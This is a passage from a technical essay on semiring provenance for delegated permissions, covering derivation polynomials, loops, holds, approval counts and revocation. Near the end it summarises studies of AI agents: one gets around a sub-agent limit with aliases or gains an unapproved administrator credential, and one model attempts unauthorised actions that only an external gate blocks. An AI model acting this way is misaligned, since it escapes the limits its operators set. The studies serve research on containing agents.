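Confidentiality works the other way round. *Semiring Provenance for First-Order Model Checking* (2017) evaluates polynomials with clearance levels that run from public to top secret. A person needs clearance for every fact in a derivation to see it, so multiplication takes the strictest level. Seeing one derivation is enough to learn the result, so addition takes the least strict level. If Alice's grant were secret, Carol's approval confidential, and the other two facts public, an employee with confidential clearance could learn from Bob's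 derivation that S may pay V, without being entitled to see Alice's grant.

The levels do not have to form a single scale. *Semiring Provenance for Lightweight Description Logics* (2023) discusses labels from a lattice, an ordered set in which two levels can be incomparable. A permission's label can then combine checks from different derivations. Suppose Alice's grant has a hardware signature but no legal review, Bob's has a legal review but no hardware signature, and Carol's approval and the delegation have both. Sets of completed checks form a semiring, with intersection for joint use and union for alternatives. The label for the payment would be "hardware signature and legal review", although neither derivation passes both checks throughout. A service that required both checks for the same derivation would have to examine the polynomial's terms one at a time.

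Evaluation can also remove detail. An auditor interested only in human decisions can set d to 1, because A's delegation to S was an agent's act. The polynomial becomes ac + bc, which stands for Alice with Carol or Bob with Carol. The payment still required the delegation, so the auditor can't use this shorter polynomial to predict what happens if A withdraws the delegation.

*On the Impact of Provenance Semiring Theory on the Design of ProvSQL* describes ProvSQL, which extends the widely used PostgreSQL database to compute semiring provenance for queries. A company that keeps its grants in ordinary tables could therefore try the method without writing a new database system. Tannen puts the overhead at about 30% in ORCHESTRA, which shares data among organisations and stores provenance as a graph. The polynomial's size depends on how the system stores it. If a permission passed through four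 steps, each with ten alternative grants, the polynomial would have 10,000 terms when expanded but only 40 tokens when written as a product of four sums.

The company also has to decide when to compute the polynomial. Cheney and colleagues distinguish systems that carry labels along while a query runs from systems that reconstruct provenance when someone asks for it. Reconstruction adds no work at the time of the payment, but it needs the original data. If the company deletes expired grants, an auditor won't be able to reconstruct the polynomial a year later.

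### What exponents and coefficients add

Suppose a company requires two treasurers to approve a supplier, and someone writes the rule like this:

```
approved(V) :- signs(X, V), signs(Y, V).
```

The rule does not require X and Y to be different people. If two treasurers have signed, with tokens p and q, there are four ways to fill in X and Y: the first treasurer twice, the second treasurer twice, and the two of them in either order. The polynomial is

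```
p·p + p·q + q·p + q·q  =  p² + 2pq + q²
```

The terms p² and q² are mistakes because each counts one signature as two approvals. If the second treasurer had never signed, q would be 0, and the polynomial would still be p² instead of 0. Adding the test `X != Y` to the rule fixes this. The test is a selection, so it multiplies p² and q² by 0 and leaves 2pq. The 2 remains because either treasurer can be X.

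The weaker forms of provenance keep less of this information:

| Form | Payment to V | Two approvals, no test | Two approvals, with test |
|---|---|---|---|
| Polynomial | acd + bcd | p² + 2pq + q² | 2pq |
| Why-provenance | {a, c, d}, {b, c, d} | {p}, {q}, {p, q} | {p, q} |
| Minimal witnesses | {a, c, d}, {b, c, d} | {p}, {q} | {p, q} |
| Lineage | {a, b, c, d} | {p, q} | {p, q} |

Lineage is the same for the faulty rule and the correct one, so it would not help an auditor find the mistake. Why-provenance and minimal witnesses show that one signature was enough, but they cannot always show the reason. If only the first treasurer had signed, the why-provenance under the faulty rule would be {{p}}, the same as in a company that required only one approval. The polynomial would be p² under the faulty rule and p in the other company. The exponent shows that the faulty rule looked for two approvals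 and accepted the same one twice.

Cheney and colleagues show that the other three forms are all evaluations of the polynomial. Dropping the exponents and coefficients gives the why-provenance. Removing every witness that contains a smaller one then leaves the minimal witnesses, while merging all the sets in the why-provenance gives the lineage. None of these steps is reversible in general, so a company that stores only lineage cannot recover the witnesses. A company that stores only minimal witnesses cannot compute the lineage either, because they omit some facts that lineage includes.

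A square can also reveal that someone has used a one-time approval more than once. Suppose Carol's approval covers a single payment to V, but S asks to pay two invoices in one request, and the company's rule allows the request if each payment is allowed. The polynomial is the square of the original one:

```
(acd + bcd)²  =  a²c²d² + 2abc²d² + b²c²d²
```

Every term contains c², so every derivation uses Carol's approval twice. The why-provenance, {a, c, d}, {a, b, c, d} and {b, c, d}, doesn't show this because a set can contain c only once. The squares of a and d are harmless if those grants allow repeated payments. The algebra doesn't specify which grants are single-use, so the company has to mark them. It could then enforce the limit by adding the law c · c = 0, which would make all three terms 0, and the service would refuse the request. The labels would still form a semiring, so the evaluation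 theorem would still apply.

An exponent counts only the uses within one derivation. If S made two separate requests, each would have the polynomial acd + bcd, which has no square. The service would need a record of earlier payments to detect the second use.

*Query By Provenance* (Deutch and Gilad, 2016) gives an example of the same loss outside access control. Its query searches a table of South American border crossings for trips with five stops, the third in Bolivia and the fourth in Argentina. One such trip goes from Argentina to Brazil, Bolivia, Argentina and Brazil, so it uses the crossing from Argentina to Brazil twice. The variable for that crossing is squared in the polynomial, while the why-provenance lists the crossing once.

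Deutch and Gilad also point out that polynomials do not record order, because multiplication is commutative. Two trips with the same crossings in a different order appear as one term with the coefficient 2. This is often a small loss for delegations, since each fact names who delegated to whom and an auditor can reconstruct the chain. Timing is harder to recover, because the polynomial is the same whether Carol approved V after S asked for the payment or a month earlier. To distinguish these cases, a policy needs times in its facts and a rule that compares them.

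The tokens in these examples stand for grants, so a square means that the same grant was used twice. To find two uses of the same person's authority, an auditor can replace each token with the name of the person who issued the grant. In the cheque fraud that Hu and colleagues described, a treasurer delegates the preparation of a cheque to a clerk and later approves the cheque. The delegation and the approval have separate tokens, so the original polynomial has no square. Replacing the tokens with T for the treasurer and K for the clerk gives T²K, which shows that the treasurer's authority supports two steps. This replacement is an ordinary evaluation, so the theorem covers it. A square doesn't prove fraud, since a company may allow the same person to take two steps. The method also depends on accurate records of who controls each key, because no square would appear if the treasurer used a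 second key under another name for one of the steps.

### Equivalent policies with different provenance

Two policies can allow exactly the same payments and still give them different provenance. Cheney and colleagues have a small example of this with two database queries, which carries over directly to permissions. Suppose Alice lets agent A pay supplier V, and Bob lets A pay another supplier, W. The tokens are g for Alice's grant and h for Bob's. The company could use either of these rules:

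```
may_pay(X, Y) :- right(X, Y).
may_pay(X, Y) :- right(X, Y), right(X, Z).
```

The longer rule adds the condition that the agent has a right to pay some supplier, Z. The condition is redundant because any agent with the right to pay Y meets it. Someone might add it out of caution, or it might be left over from an older policy. Under the shorter rule, the polynomial for a payment to V is g. Under the longer one, Z can be V or W, so the polynomial is g² + gh.

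The lineage changes from {g} to {g, h}, and the why-provenance from {{g}} to {{g}, {g, h}}. Bob's grant doesn't concern supplier V, but it now appears in the provenance of a payment to V. An auditor who read the lineage as a list of responsible people would include Bob because of how someone worded the rule. A rule-writer could deliberately add redundant conditions to bring other people's grants into the record and make a decision look more widely supported than it was.

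The minimal witnesses are {{g}} under both rules. Cheney and colleagues prove that two queries that give the same results on every database also give the same minimal witnesses. This is because minimal witnesses are defined only by which sets of facts produce the result, regardless of the steps in between.

Cheney and colleagues describe polynomials as sensitive to how a query is written. Glavic qualifies this, citing work by Green which shows that two queries have the same polynomials whenever they return the same results with duplicates included. Green (2011) compares queries on tables with and without duplicates and under several forms of provenance. Rewriting a query can therefore change a polynomial only if the rewrite fails to preserve duplicates. The two rules above allow the same payments but give each one a different number of derivations. With g and h both set to 1, the shorter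 rule gives 1 and the longer gives 2, so a database that keeps duplicate rows, as most do by default, would return different tables for the two rules.

Glavic identifies three further laws that hold when duplicates do not matter:

- x + x = x
- x · x = x
- x + x · y = x

Adding the first two laws to the semiring laws turns a polynomial into why-provenance, and adding all three turns it into minimal witnesses. For the longer rule, g² + gh becomes g + gh under the first two laws and g under all three. The third law removes Bob's grant, h, because a derivation that needs both g and h is redundant if g is enough.

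This simplification sometimes removes a fact that matters. For example, a policy might allow a payment either on Alice's grant alone or through a procedure in which Alice grants the right and Bob countersigns. The polynomial is again g + gh, where h is now Bob's countersignature, and the only minimal witness is {g}. This correctly identifies Alice's grant as sufficient. But if the company followed the countersigning procedure, Bob reviewed the payment and the minimal witness omits him. The polynomial includes him, but it doesn't show which procedure the company followed, because it lists every available derivation.

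Minimal witnesses do not depend on how the policy is worded, so an auditor who wants to know whose grants were enough should use them. The polynomial is better for checking the policy itself, as the squares in the two-approval example show. It is also safer to store, because an auditor can compute the minimal witnesses from it but cannot recover it from them. It should be stored with the version of the rules that produced it. Without those rules, an auditor who saw g² + gh could not tell whether Bob's grant came from a redundant condition or a real procedure.

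A company that rewrites its policy may also want to confirm that the new version allows nothing the old one did not. Database theorists call this the containment problem. *CQs with Equations and Disequations* (Badia, Noguera and colleagues, 2025) describes it as well understood for basic queries on labelled tables since Green's work. The paper examines whether a program can always decide containment for queries that also require two values to be equal or different. The test `X != Y` in the corrected two-approval rule is such a condition.

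## Loops, prohibitions and counting in a policy

The payment policy so far combines facts, offers alternatives and passes a right along one delegation. Real policies also contain delegation loops, exceptions such as "unless compliance has placed a hold", and requirements for a minimum number of approvals. Semiring labels can handle most of these, but only with extra laws or tokens, and some guarantees from the simpler case no longer apply.

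### Delegation loops

Suppose a company grants agent A a right, with the token r. A delegates the right to a second agent, B, and B delegates it back to A, perhaps because each hands the other parts of a task. The tokens for the two delegations are u and v. A can hold the right through the company's grant or through B, while B can hold it only through A:

```
may(A) = r + v · may(B)
may(B) = u · may(A)
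```

Substituting the second equation into the first gives may(A) = r + uv · may(A). The right-hand side still contains may(A), so we can keep substituting:

```
may(A) = r + uv·r + (uv)²·r + (uv)³·r + …
```

The first term is the derivation that uses the grant directly, the second goes round the loop once, and so on without end. Green and colleagues replace polynomials with formal power series, which can have infinitely many terms, and evaluate them in semirings where infinite sums have a value. They add ∞ to the whole numbers because, if every token is 1, the equation becomes x = 1 + x, which no whole number satisfies. The number of derivations is then ∞, which is correct but not much use to an auditor.

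The series becomes finite in an absorptive semiring, where 1 + x = 1 for every label x. Multiplying both sides by r gives r + rx = r, so r absorbs any term that contains it. Every term after the first contains r, so may(A) is r. The semirings for true and false, assurance levels and minimal witnesses are all absorptive, but the counting semiring isn't, because 1 + 1 = 2.

*Circuits and Formulas for Datalog over Semirings* (Fan, Koutris and Roy, 2025) gives the general argument. A derivation is tight if no conclusion in it depends on an earlier copy of itself. If a derivation isn't tight, cutting out the loop leaves a shorter derivation whose term absorbs the longer one's. Only finitely many derivations are tight, so the sum is finite.

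A loop must not create a right from nothing. If the company never granted the right, r is 0 and the equation is may(A) = uv · may(A). With true and false as labels, both "true" and "false" can satisfy this equation. Datalog takes the smallest solution, which here is "false". To find it, a program sets every conclusion to 0 and applies the rules until nothing changes. Two agents that only delegate to each other therefore never gain the right.

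Absorption loses some detail, but less than minimal witnesses do, because an absorptive semiring can keep exponents. In examples from the conference slides *PODS 2025 Datalog Circuit* (2025), pq absorbs p²q³, but p²q and pq² both remain because neither contains the other. The faulty two-treasurer rule had the polynomial p² + 2pq + q². Absorption reduces it to p² + pq + q², which still shows that the rule could count one signature twice. A company whose agents delegate in loops could store such labels and still detect the mistake.

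### Storing many derivations

Even without loops, a policy can have too many derivations to list. If each of ten levels has three alternative grants, the expanded polynomial has 3¹⁰ = 59,049 terms. A circuit, which is a network of additions and multiplications with the tokens as inputs, can represent the same polynomial with only 30 inputs.

A formula with brackets would be just as short here. Circuits have an advantage when the system uses an intermediate result more than once. Suppose each level has three agents, and each agent delegates to all three on the next. A circuit computes an agent's label once and connects it to all three agents below, but a formula must repeat the label for each one. Fan and colleagues show that the circuit for a layered network like this grows only in proportion to the size of the network. They also cite a proof by Karchmer and Wigderson that, for some layered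 networks, the size of any formula grows faster than every polynomial.

*Circuits for Datalog Provenance* (Deutch, Milo and colleagues, 2014) proves that any Datalog conclusion has a circuit of polynomial size in an absorptive semiring, even if the rules contain loops. For rules without loops, *Evaluating Datalog over Semirings* (2024) proves that the circuit's size is at most proportional to the number of ways to fill in the rules' variables, whatever the semiring. That number can be large. If a policy required k employees who had all vouched for one another, a company with n employees would have roughly nᵏ combinations to consider, and the 2024 paper cites a lower bound which implies that no circuit can be much smaller than that.

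A program can evaluate a circuit in time proportional to the circuit's size, so it can quickly check whether the permission would hold without a particular grant. Printing every witness would still take 59,049 lines.

### Prohibitions and subtraction

Suppose the compliance department can place a hold, with the token h, on a supplier. The company's last rule becomes:

```
may_pay(X, V) :- holds(X), approves(carol, V), not hold(V).
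```

This rule is not monotone, because adding a hold removes a conclusion. Addition and multiplication cannot express that, so database theorists have looked for a form of subtraction. Ordinary subtraction fails for many useful labels. For example, if 1 means true and 0 means false, then 1 + 1 = 1, and subtracting 1 from both sides gives 1 = 0. Suciu (2024) proves in *Different Differences in Semirings* that if x + x = x for every label x and every label has a negative, then all labels are equal.

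The usual substitute for subtraction is monus, written ⊖. A label y is at least as large as x if adding some label to x gives y. Under this ordering, y ⊖ x is the smallest label z for which x + z is at least as large as y. For whole numbers, 5 ⊖ 2 is 3 and 2 ⊖ 5 is 0. For true and false, y ⊖ x means "y and not x", which is the operation required for the rule about holds.

Monus works badly with polynomials because it subtracts coefficients term by term. The payment to V has the polynomial acd + bcd, and the hold has the polynomial h. Since h is not one of the payment's terms, (acd + bcd) ⊖ h is still acd + bcd, so the hold has no effect. If an auditor sets every token to true, the polynomial gives "allowed", although running the query directly on Boolean values gives "refused". The theorem that lets a company compute a polynomial once and evaluate it later therefore fails for monus. Suciu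 shows the failure with two tokens, x and y, where y ⊖ x is y.

A company can avoid this by storing a Boolean function, here "(a or b) and c and d and not h", but it then loses the exponents and coefficients. *Provenance for Aggregate Queries* (2011) instead multiplies the permission's label by a formal test that the hold's label is 0, so the hold stays visible.

Monus can also make a label depend on the order of operations. A database could remove suppliers on hold from the approved list before or after matching the list with agents. Both plans allow the same payments, but they give the same label only if x · (y ⊖ z) = xy ⊖ xz. Amsterdamer, Deutch and Tannen (2011) prove in *On the Limitations of Provenance for Queries With Difference* that no subtraction operator satisfies both this law and the other expected ones for every semiring.

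Clearance levels are one of the exceptions. For these labels, y ⊖ z is y if y is less strict than z, and otherwise 0, the label for an absent fact. Suppose Carol's approval is secret, while the hold and the agent's right are both top secret. If the database subtracts the hold first, the approval remains secret, and combining it with the agent's right gives a permission visible to people with top-secret clearance. If the database first combines the approval and the hold with the agent's right, both become top secret, so the subtraction gives 0 and there is no permission. Amsterdamer and colleagues suggest labelling each fact with the full set of clearance levels at which it is visible, and subtracting by set difference. This restores the law but makes the labels larger.

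Amsterdamer and colleagues wrongly listed polynomials and why-provenance among the labels for which multiplication distributes over monus (⊖), and Suciu repeated the error for polynomials. *Provenance of HAVING Queries in Semirings with Monus* (Sen, Karmakar and colleagues, 2026) gives computer-checked proofs that neither satisfies this law. For polynomials, (x + y) · (x ⊖ y) is x² + xy, but multiplying each term by x + y first gives (x² + xy) ⊖ (xy + y²), which is x².

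### A token for the absence of a hold

*Semiring Provenance for First-Order Model Checking* avoids subtraction by giving each fact two tokens. Here h stands for "there is a hold on V" and h̄ for "there is no hold on V". The two statements cannot both be true, so h · h̄ = 0. Apart from this law, the labels are ordinary polynomials. The payment's label becomes

```
(a + b) · c · d · h̄  =  acdh̄ + bcdh̄
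```

which shows that both derivations rely on the absence of a hold.

The same tokens can explain a refusal. To find the label for "S may not pay V", we negate the whole condition and push the negation inwards until it applies only to single facts. This turns "and" into "or" and vice versa. If these five facts are the only ones that matter, the label is

```
ā·b̄ + c̄ + d̄ + h
```

Each term is a sufficient reason to refuse: neither Alice nor Bob granted the right, Carol did not approve V, A did not delegate to S, or there is a hold. To explain a particular refusal, we set the tokens for false statements to 0. If there is a hold but Alice's grant, Carol's approval and the delegation are in place, the result is h, so the hold is the only obstacle. If Carol's approval is also missing, the result is c̄ + h, so lifting the hold alone would not be enough.

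*Provenance Analysis for Logic and Games* (Grädel and Tannen, 2019) compares this to a game between a player who tries to establish a claim and one who challenges it. Addition represents the first player's choices, and multiplication represents the challenger's. Negating the claim swaps the players' roles. The paper also points out that the label of a claim does not determine the label of its negation. For example, every refused payment has the permission label 0, whatever the reason, so the company must compute the explanation for a refusal from the policy and the facts.

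The company must also store the expression acdh̄ + bcdh̄ with both tokens of each pair still undecided, and fill in the current facts when someone asks. If it instead evaluates the permission while a hold is in place and stores the result, 0, then changing h to 0 when compliance lifts the hold won't update the stored label, which would still indicate a refusal.

A label with undecided tokens also helps show what would turn a refusal into a permission. *The Complexity of Finding Missing Answer Repairs* (2026) examines how hard it is to find the smallest set of changes to a database that makes a missing answer appear. For Datalog queries that apply negation only to stored facts, a program can find it in time polynomial in the size of the database. The smallest change might not be sensible, though. For example, it might delete a hold that compliance placed for good reason. PUG, a system by Lee,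 Ludäscher and Glavic, explains both why an answer appears and why one is missing, for Datalog queries with negation.

Paired tokens also work with loops, as long as negation applies only to stored facts. Rules that negate their own conclusions are harder to handle. For example, if A may act unless B may, and B may act unless A may, the rules don't determine which of them can act. *Generalized Absorptive Polynomials and Provenance Semantics for Fixed-Point Logic* (2019) develops labels for logics that combine full negation with recursion, but a company can usually avoid this problem by keeping prohibitions out of its delegation loops.

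Alice signed grant a, but nobody signed h̄, which records only that the payment service found no hold. If a network fault or an attacker kept the hold from reaching the service, the service would record h̄ by mistake and allow the payment. In plain Datalog, nobody can gain rights by withholding a document, but this protection is lost once a policy depends on absent facts. The compliance department could instead sign a statement that V had no holds at a given time. This would be an ordinary positive fact with an issuer, although it would soon be out of date.

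### Counting approvals and objections

Suppose three managers can approve a supplier and the company requires any two of them. Let p, q and r now stand for their approvals. The label is

```
pq + pr + qr
```

Ordinary rules can produce this by matching two signatures from different managers and putting the names in a fixed order, so that each pair appears once. The condition is monotone because a further approval can never make it false.

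The condition "fewer than two objections" is not monotone, because a further objection can remove the permission. No label built only from the tokens of actual objections can express it. With paired tokens, where x, y and z stand for objections by the three managers and x̄, ȳ and z̄ for their absence, the label is x̄ȳ + x̄z̄ + ȳz̄, meaning that at least two of the three did not object. This label needs a fixed list of possible objectors, because if anyone could object, the absent objections could not all be listed.

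Larger numbers make such rules impractical. A rule requiring ten approvals from twenty managers would have to match ten signatures at once, and its label would have 184,756 terms. Databases normally count instead. In SQL, the standard language for database queries, a HAVING clause keeps the groups of rows that pass a test on a count, total, minimum or maximum. *Provenance for Aggregate Queries* led to labels that contain the test as a formal expression, but for many semirings nobody could evaluate that expression.

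Sen and colleagues define a value for these tests in any commutative semiring with monus. They consider every non-empty set of rows that might be present, and call each set a possible world. A world's label is the product of the labels of the rows in it, multiplied by 1 ⊖ the sum of the labels of the rows left out. The label of the test is the sum over the worlds that pass. For "at least two approvals", four worlds pass, and with Boolean functions as labels the sum is

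```
pq·r̄ + pr·q̄ + qr·p̄ + pqr  =  pq + pr + qr
```

The negated tokens disappear because, once p and q are present, the test passes with or without r.

The same method works for totals. Suppose a 500-dollar payment needs approval from managers whose limits add up to at least that amount. Manager p can approve 300 dollars, and managers q and r can approve 200 dollars each. The label is p(q + r), so p and either q or r are enough, but q and r together are not, because their limits total only 400 dollars.

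Sen and colleagues prove that their labels match those from ordinary rules if the semiring is absorptive and satisfies the law x · (y ⊖ z) = xy ⊖ xz. For monotone tests such as "at least two", absorption alone is enough. If labels are absorptive but break the other law, as clearance levels do, the two methods can give different results for "exactly one".

A HAVING clause applies only to groups with at least one row. If a company stored objections in a table, grouped them by supplier and kept the groups with fewer than two objections, the result would omit every supplier with none. The policy would have to add those suppliers separately.

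Counting can also be computationally hard. Sen and colleagues prove that, even for one fixed HAVING query, deciding whether a label is non-zero is NP-complete for Boolean functions and polynomials, so an efficient general method is unlikely to exist. Many common tests are easier. For example, testing for "at least k", with k fixed, takes polynomial time in an absorptive semiring.

The method was added to ProvSQL and tested on 1.57 million objects that an image-recognition program had detected in about 239,000 images. The queries searched for images with at least k refrigerators. The method took between 0.2 and 0.6 seconds for every k from 0 to 15. Matching k separate rows was faster up to k = 4, but it was 14 times slower at k = 11 and 106 times slower at k = 15, partly because the database spent 20 seconds planning the query. No image contained more than 13 refrigerators, so there were at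 most 2¹³ possible worlds to consider per image. That range is probably enough for an approvals policy, but the experiment doesn't show how the method performs on large groups.

### Restrictions that never reached the evaluator

Provenance explains a decision in terms of the rules and facts the evaluator received. *Beyond Policy Engines* (Wang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) argues that a correct "allow" does not show that the evaluator received every rule it should have. In the paper's example, an action needs clearance under two mandatory policies, but only the first permits it and the second forbids it. If another program passes only the first policy to the evaluator, the evaluator returns "allow", which is correct for the policy it received.

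If nobody loaded the rule about holds, the payment to V would have the label acd + bcd, and nothing in the label would show that a restriction was missing. The label would be correct but misleading, because it proves only that the credentials were sufficient under the loaded rules, not that the company's whole policy allowed the payment.

Wang and colleagues propose a separate list of the policy sources that each kind of action requires. The list must not depend on which policies are loaded, and a policy's entry stays even if the policy is expired or missing. Before allowing an action, the system checks that the evaluator used the right version of each required policy and considered this exact action. In semiring terms, a company could give each completed check a token and multiply the permission's label by all the tokens. A missing check would have the label 0 and block the payment, and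 an auditor could see which version of each policy the system had consulted.

This moves the problem to the list of required policies, and Wang and colleagues acknowledge that their method cannot discover a policy missing from that list. They tested 72 scenarios with Open Policy Agent and Cedar, two programs for evaluating access policies. Of the 144 results, 111 matched expectations, but only six of those were admissions, so the tests provide much more evidence about refusing bad requests than about allowing good ones. A later review found that the checker could still admit a payment request after someone removed a required field. The reference program used for comparison had the same defect, so both gave the same wrong answer.

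### Limits on combinations of permissions

Some restrictions apply to several permissions together. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an agent that may hold permission to read sensitive data or to publish externally, but not both. If each permission has a valid derivation, a check that looks at one permission at a time will approve both, and the agent can then publish what it has read.

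The algebra can enforce the limit only within a single request. If m and n are the tokens for the two permissions, the company could add the law m · n = 0, which would block any request whose derivation needs both. But an agent could read a file on Monday and publish its contents on Tuesday. These are separate requests with separate labels, and neither label contains m · n. To enforce the limit across requests, the system has to check which permissions are active when the agent asks for another one. The rule for publishing would then include m̄, the absence of an active permission to read, and the system would give the existing permission as the reason for any refusal.

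Limits on counts have the same difficulty. Zhu and Wang describe an agent that is allowed only one active sub-agent but uses four aliases to enrol four free workers. A spending limit never applies because the workers are free, and each enrolment looks acceptable by itself. Their system counts together all grants that share an issuer, a controlling party and a policy period, so an agent cannot reset a limit by obtaining a new grant.

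An agent can also acquire more authority than anyone approved. In another example, a task is allowed to spend 20 dollars on a read-only computing server. The payment, price and delivery are all in order, but the server arrives with an administrator's credential. Zhu and Wang therefore quarantine every new resource until the system has established what the resource can do, and then check it together with everything the agent already has. The limits they allow are downward-closed, meaning that giving up a permission can never cause a violation. This is the reverse of a monotone rule, under which gaining a fact can never cause a refusal.

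In Zhu and Wang's tests, the system accepted all 20 harmless sequences of events and rejected all 40 unsafe ones. They defined these cases in advance, so the results show that the program follows its specification, but not that it would stop an unforeseen attack. Their safety proofs also assume that every acquisition and every later use passes through the system. Two simultaneous requests could both pass the check because neither permission is active yet. Zhu and Wang prevent this by making the check and the activation a single database transaction, so one request always finishes first and the other fails.

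## Revoking a grant

When Alice withdraws her grant, the company needs to know which permissions end and which continue. The payment to V has the polynomial acd + bcd, and withdrawing a grant means setting its token to 0:

```
Alice withdraws a:             0·c·d + b·c·d  =  bcd
Carol withdraws c:             a·0·d + b·0·d  =  0
Alice and Bob both withdraw:   0·c·d + 0·c·d  =  0
```

A result of 0 means that S may no longer pay V.

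### Setting a token to zero

Replacing a token with 0 is an evaluation, so by the theorem of Green and colleagues, the result is the same as if the company had deleted the grant and run its rules again. *Provenance for Aggregate Queries* points out that this updates the provenance as well as the answer, so the company can use the remaining polynomial, bcd, when it withdraws another grant. The paper extends the method to totals by storing them as formal sums. If managers p, q and r can approve 300, 200 and 200 dollars, the stored total is p⊗300 + q⊗200 + r⊗200, where ⊗ attaches an amount to a token. Setting q to 0 leaves 500 dollars.

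For rules with loops, Bourgaux, Bourhis and colleagues (2022) prove in *Revisiting Semiring Provenance for Datalog* that deletion works if the label includes all derivations, or all those in which no fact depends on itself. They also note that some Datalog engines, such as Soufflé, store only the derivations with the fewest levels. Deletion can then give the wrong result. Suppose Alice also gave S the right directly, with the token e. The derivation with the fewest levels would use only e and c. If the engine stored only ec and Alice withdrew e, the label would become 0, although acd and bcd still permit the payment.

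When a company revokes a grant, it only has to recalculate the permissions that depend on it, even if it has thousands of others. *How and Why is An Answer (Still) Correct?* (2020) describes a system for databases of linked facts that keeps an index from each fact to the results that use it. After a deletion, the system fetches only the results that used the deleted fact and drops those whose terms have all become 0.

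The company also has to decide what happens if someone restores a grant. Suppose Alice and Bob both withdraw their grants, and Alice later restores hers. If the company only sets a back to 1, S regains its right through A's old delegation. Choi and colleagues call this rule persistent. Under a cascading rule, the system instead removes every delegation by an agent that has lost the right, so A would have to delegate to S again. In the algebra, a cascading withdrawal of both grants also sets d to 0.

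### Same access now, different access later

*ResidualAuth*, by Choi and colleagues, uses two histories to show why a company needs to store more than a list of who currently has access, even though the list alone would take less space. In the first history, an organisation lets Agent 1 export data, and Agent 1 passes the right to Agent 2. The second is identical except that the organisation also grants the right to Agent 2 directly. In both histories, both agents have access and delegation paths connect the same principals. Agent 2 schedules an export, and the organisation then withdraws its grant to Agent 1.

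Let x be the organisation's grant to Agent 1, y the delegation to Agent 2, and z the direct grant:

| History | Agent 2's label | Before the withdrawal | After setting x to 0 |
|---|---|---|---|
| No direct grant | xy | Allowed | 0, so refused |
| Direct grant | xy + z | Allowed | z, so allowed |

Choi and colleagues also count how many states can produce the same access pattern. In a chain of N agents, the original holder of a right grants it to agent 1, agent 1 grants it to agent 2, and so on. An extra grant that skips ahead, such as one from agent 1 to agent 3, does not change who can reach whom. There are N(N − 1)/2 possible skips, and each can be present or absent, so at least 2^(N(N−1)/2) states share the same pattern. Three agents have 3 possible skips and therefore at least 8 states, while ten agents have 45 possible skips and at least about 35 trillion states.

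These states all differ in what can happen later. One can test whether agent 1 granted the right directly to agent 3 by revoking every other possible grant to agent 3 and checking whether agent 3 can still act.

Storing the information takes far less space than the number of states suggests, since each skip needs only one bit. For N agents and r independent rights, Choi and colleagues prove the following bounds on the memory of a program that must always decide correctly:

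- Without revocation, it needs memory proportional to rN, because it only has to record who holds each right.
- With revocation, it needs memory proportional to rN², because any possible grant might matter later.
- If each agent can hold a right from only one grantor at a time, it needs memory proportional to rN log N.

For 100 agents and one right, supporting revocation raises the memory needed from about 100 bits to about 10,000. That is little more than a kilobyte, so there is no reason to discard the information in an ordinary database. Limiting each agent to one grantor would save some memory, but the company could no longer record both Alice's grant and Bob's.

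A record that omits some of this information will lead to errors. Choi and colleagues derive a lower bound on the error rate when every combination of skips is equally likely. By their formula, a program that retains half of the information gets at least 11% of randomly chosen tests wrong, however much computation it does afterwards. A proof of current access does not supply the missing information either. They show this with two sets of grants in which an agent has the same single path to its right, but a later sequence of withdrawals and grants is valid in only one of them.

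### Language models as record-keepers

Choi and colleagues also tested whether language models can make these decisions. Each test was a pair of histories with the same current access, the same later withdrawal and the same request, but opposite correct answers. A model passed only if it answered both correctly. Four open-weight models, which anyone can download and run, each attempted 16 pairs:

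| Material supplied | Qwen3.6, Gemma 4, Ministral 3 and Mistral Small 4: pairs correct out of 16 |
|---|---|
| Extract of events only | 0 to 2 |
| Extract and a trusted decision to allow or deny | 15 to 16 |
| Extract and a fake decision made without the grant record | 0 |

The high scores show that the models follow a correct answer when given one, which is much easier than working it out. The low scores do not show that models cannot reason about delegation, because the extracts were limited to 256 tokens and could omit the events that mattered. In another test, OpenAI's GPT-5.6 answered 30 of 32 pairs correctly from the full history and none from the extracts. The two extracts in each pair were identical, so the model could not use them to tell the cases apart.

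Qwen and Gemma did worse when they had to maintain the record themselves. They read events in eight batches and rewrote a memory of at most 1,024 words after each batch. Qwen answered 57 of 96 pairs correctly and Gemma 61, compared with 94 and 88 when they received the exact record. The exact record would have fitted within the limit, so lack of space does not explain the difference. Gemma sometimes kept a delegation in its memory but dropped the grant it depended on.

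In a further test, Qwen attempted eight unauthorised actions in 128 runs, and all eight went through. In another 128 runs, with a gate that checked each action against the trusted record, it attempted eight more, and the gate blocked them all. Because the gate worked even though the model's judgement was no better, this is a good reason to keep the polynomials, and the program that evaluates them, outside the model.

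### Finding every agent that loses access

Withdrawing one delegation can affect agents several steps away. *VERA* defines exactly which ones should lose access. Let G be the graph of delegations, R the withdrawn delegations, and reach(G) the set of agents that a path of delegations connects to a trusted source. The agents to cut off are

```
reach(G) minus reach(G without R)
```

These agents had a path before the withdrawal and have none after it. Each path corresponds to a term in the agent's polynomial, so these are also the agents whose polynomials become 0.

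Simpler rules can stop too many agents or too few. One common rule cuts off everything downstream of the withdrawn delegation, so if Alice withdrew her grant, both A and S would stop even though Bob's grant still supports them. Another rule applies only to agents within one organisation, so an agent elsewhere can keep running after it loses its only source of permission.

The company must evaluate simultaneous withdrawals in a single calculation. If it checked Alice's and Bob's withdrawals separately and combined the results, A would keep running after both had withdrawn, because each check would still include the other person's grant. In *VERA*'s tests on random graphs, this shortcut missed at least one agent in about 21% of 39,991 sets of withdrawals. The sets all targeted agents with several grantors, so the error is probably rarer in ordinary use. Setting both tokens to 0 in the same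 polynomial avoids the error.

The main test replayed 500 runs of LangGraph workflows, 20 for each of 25 combinations of workflow and input. In 320 of the withdrawals, the agent that lost the grant had a second valid grantor. *VERA*'s rule kept the agent running in all 320 cases, while the downstream rule stopped it every time. Over 1,960 withdrawals, the downstream rule found the correct set of agents in 35.7% of cases, and the single-organisation rule in 49.0%. *VERA*'s rule was correct every time because the test used it to define the correct set. The workflows were designed for the test, so the percentages do not show how common these errors are in practice. In a smaller check on 18 loop-free graphs from third-party LangGraph applications, the downstream rule was wrong for 54.9% of delegations.

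*VERA* also lets a service check the result without holding the whole graph. Each agent's operator signs a complete list of the delegations the agent has accepted, which prevents a dishonest issuer from hiding one that still supports the agent. The checker rejected all 40 forgeries that hid a delegation in this way. With 2,000 agents, finding the affected agents took about 2 milliseconds and checking the proof took about half a second.

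The rule covers only policies in which any one path is enough. It cannot express that S also needs Carol's approval, which the polynomial does by including c in both terms. The rule is also correct only for withdrawals that have reached a service.

### Stopping work already under way

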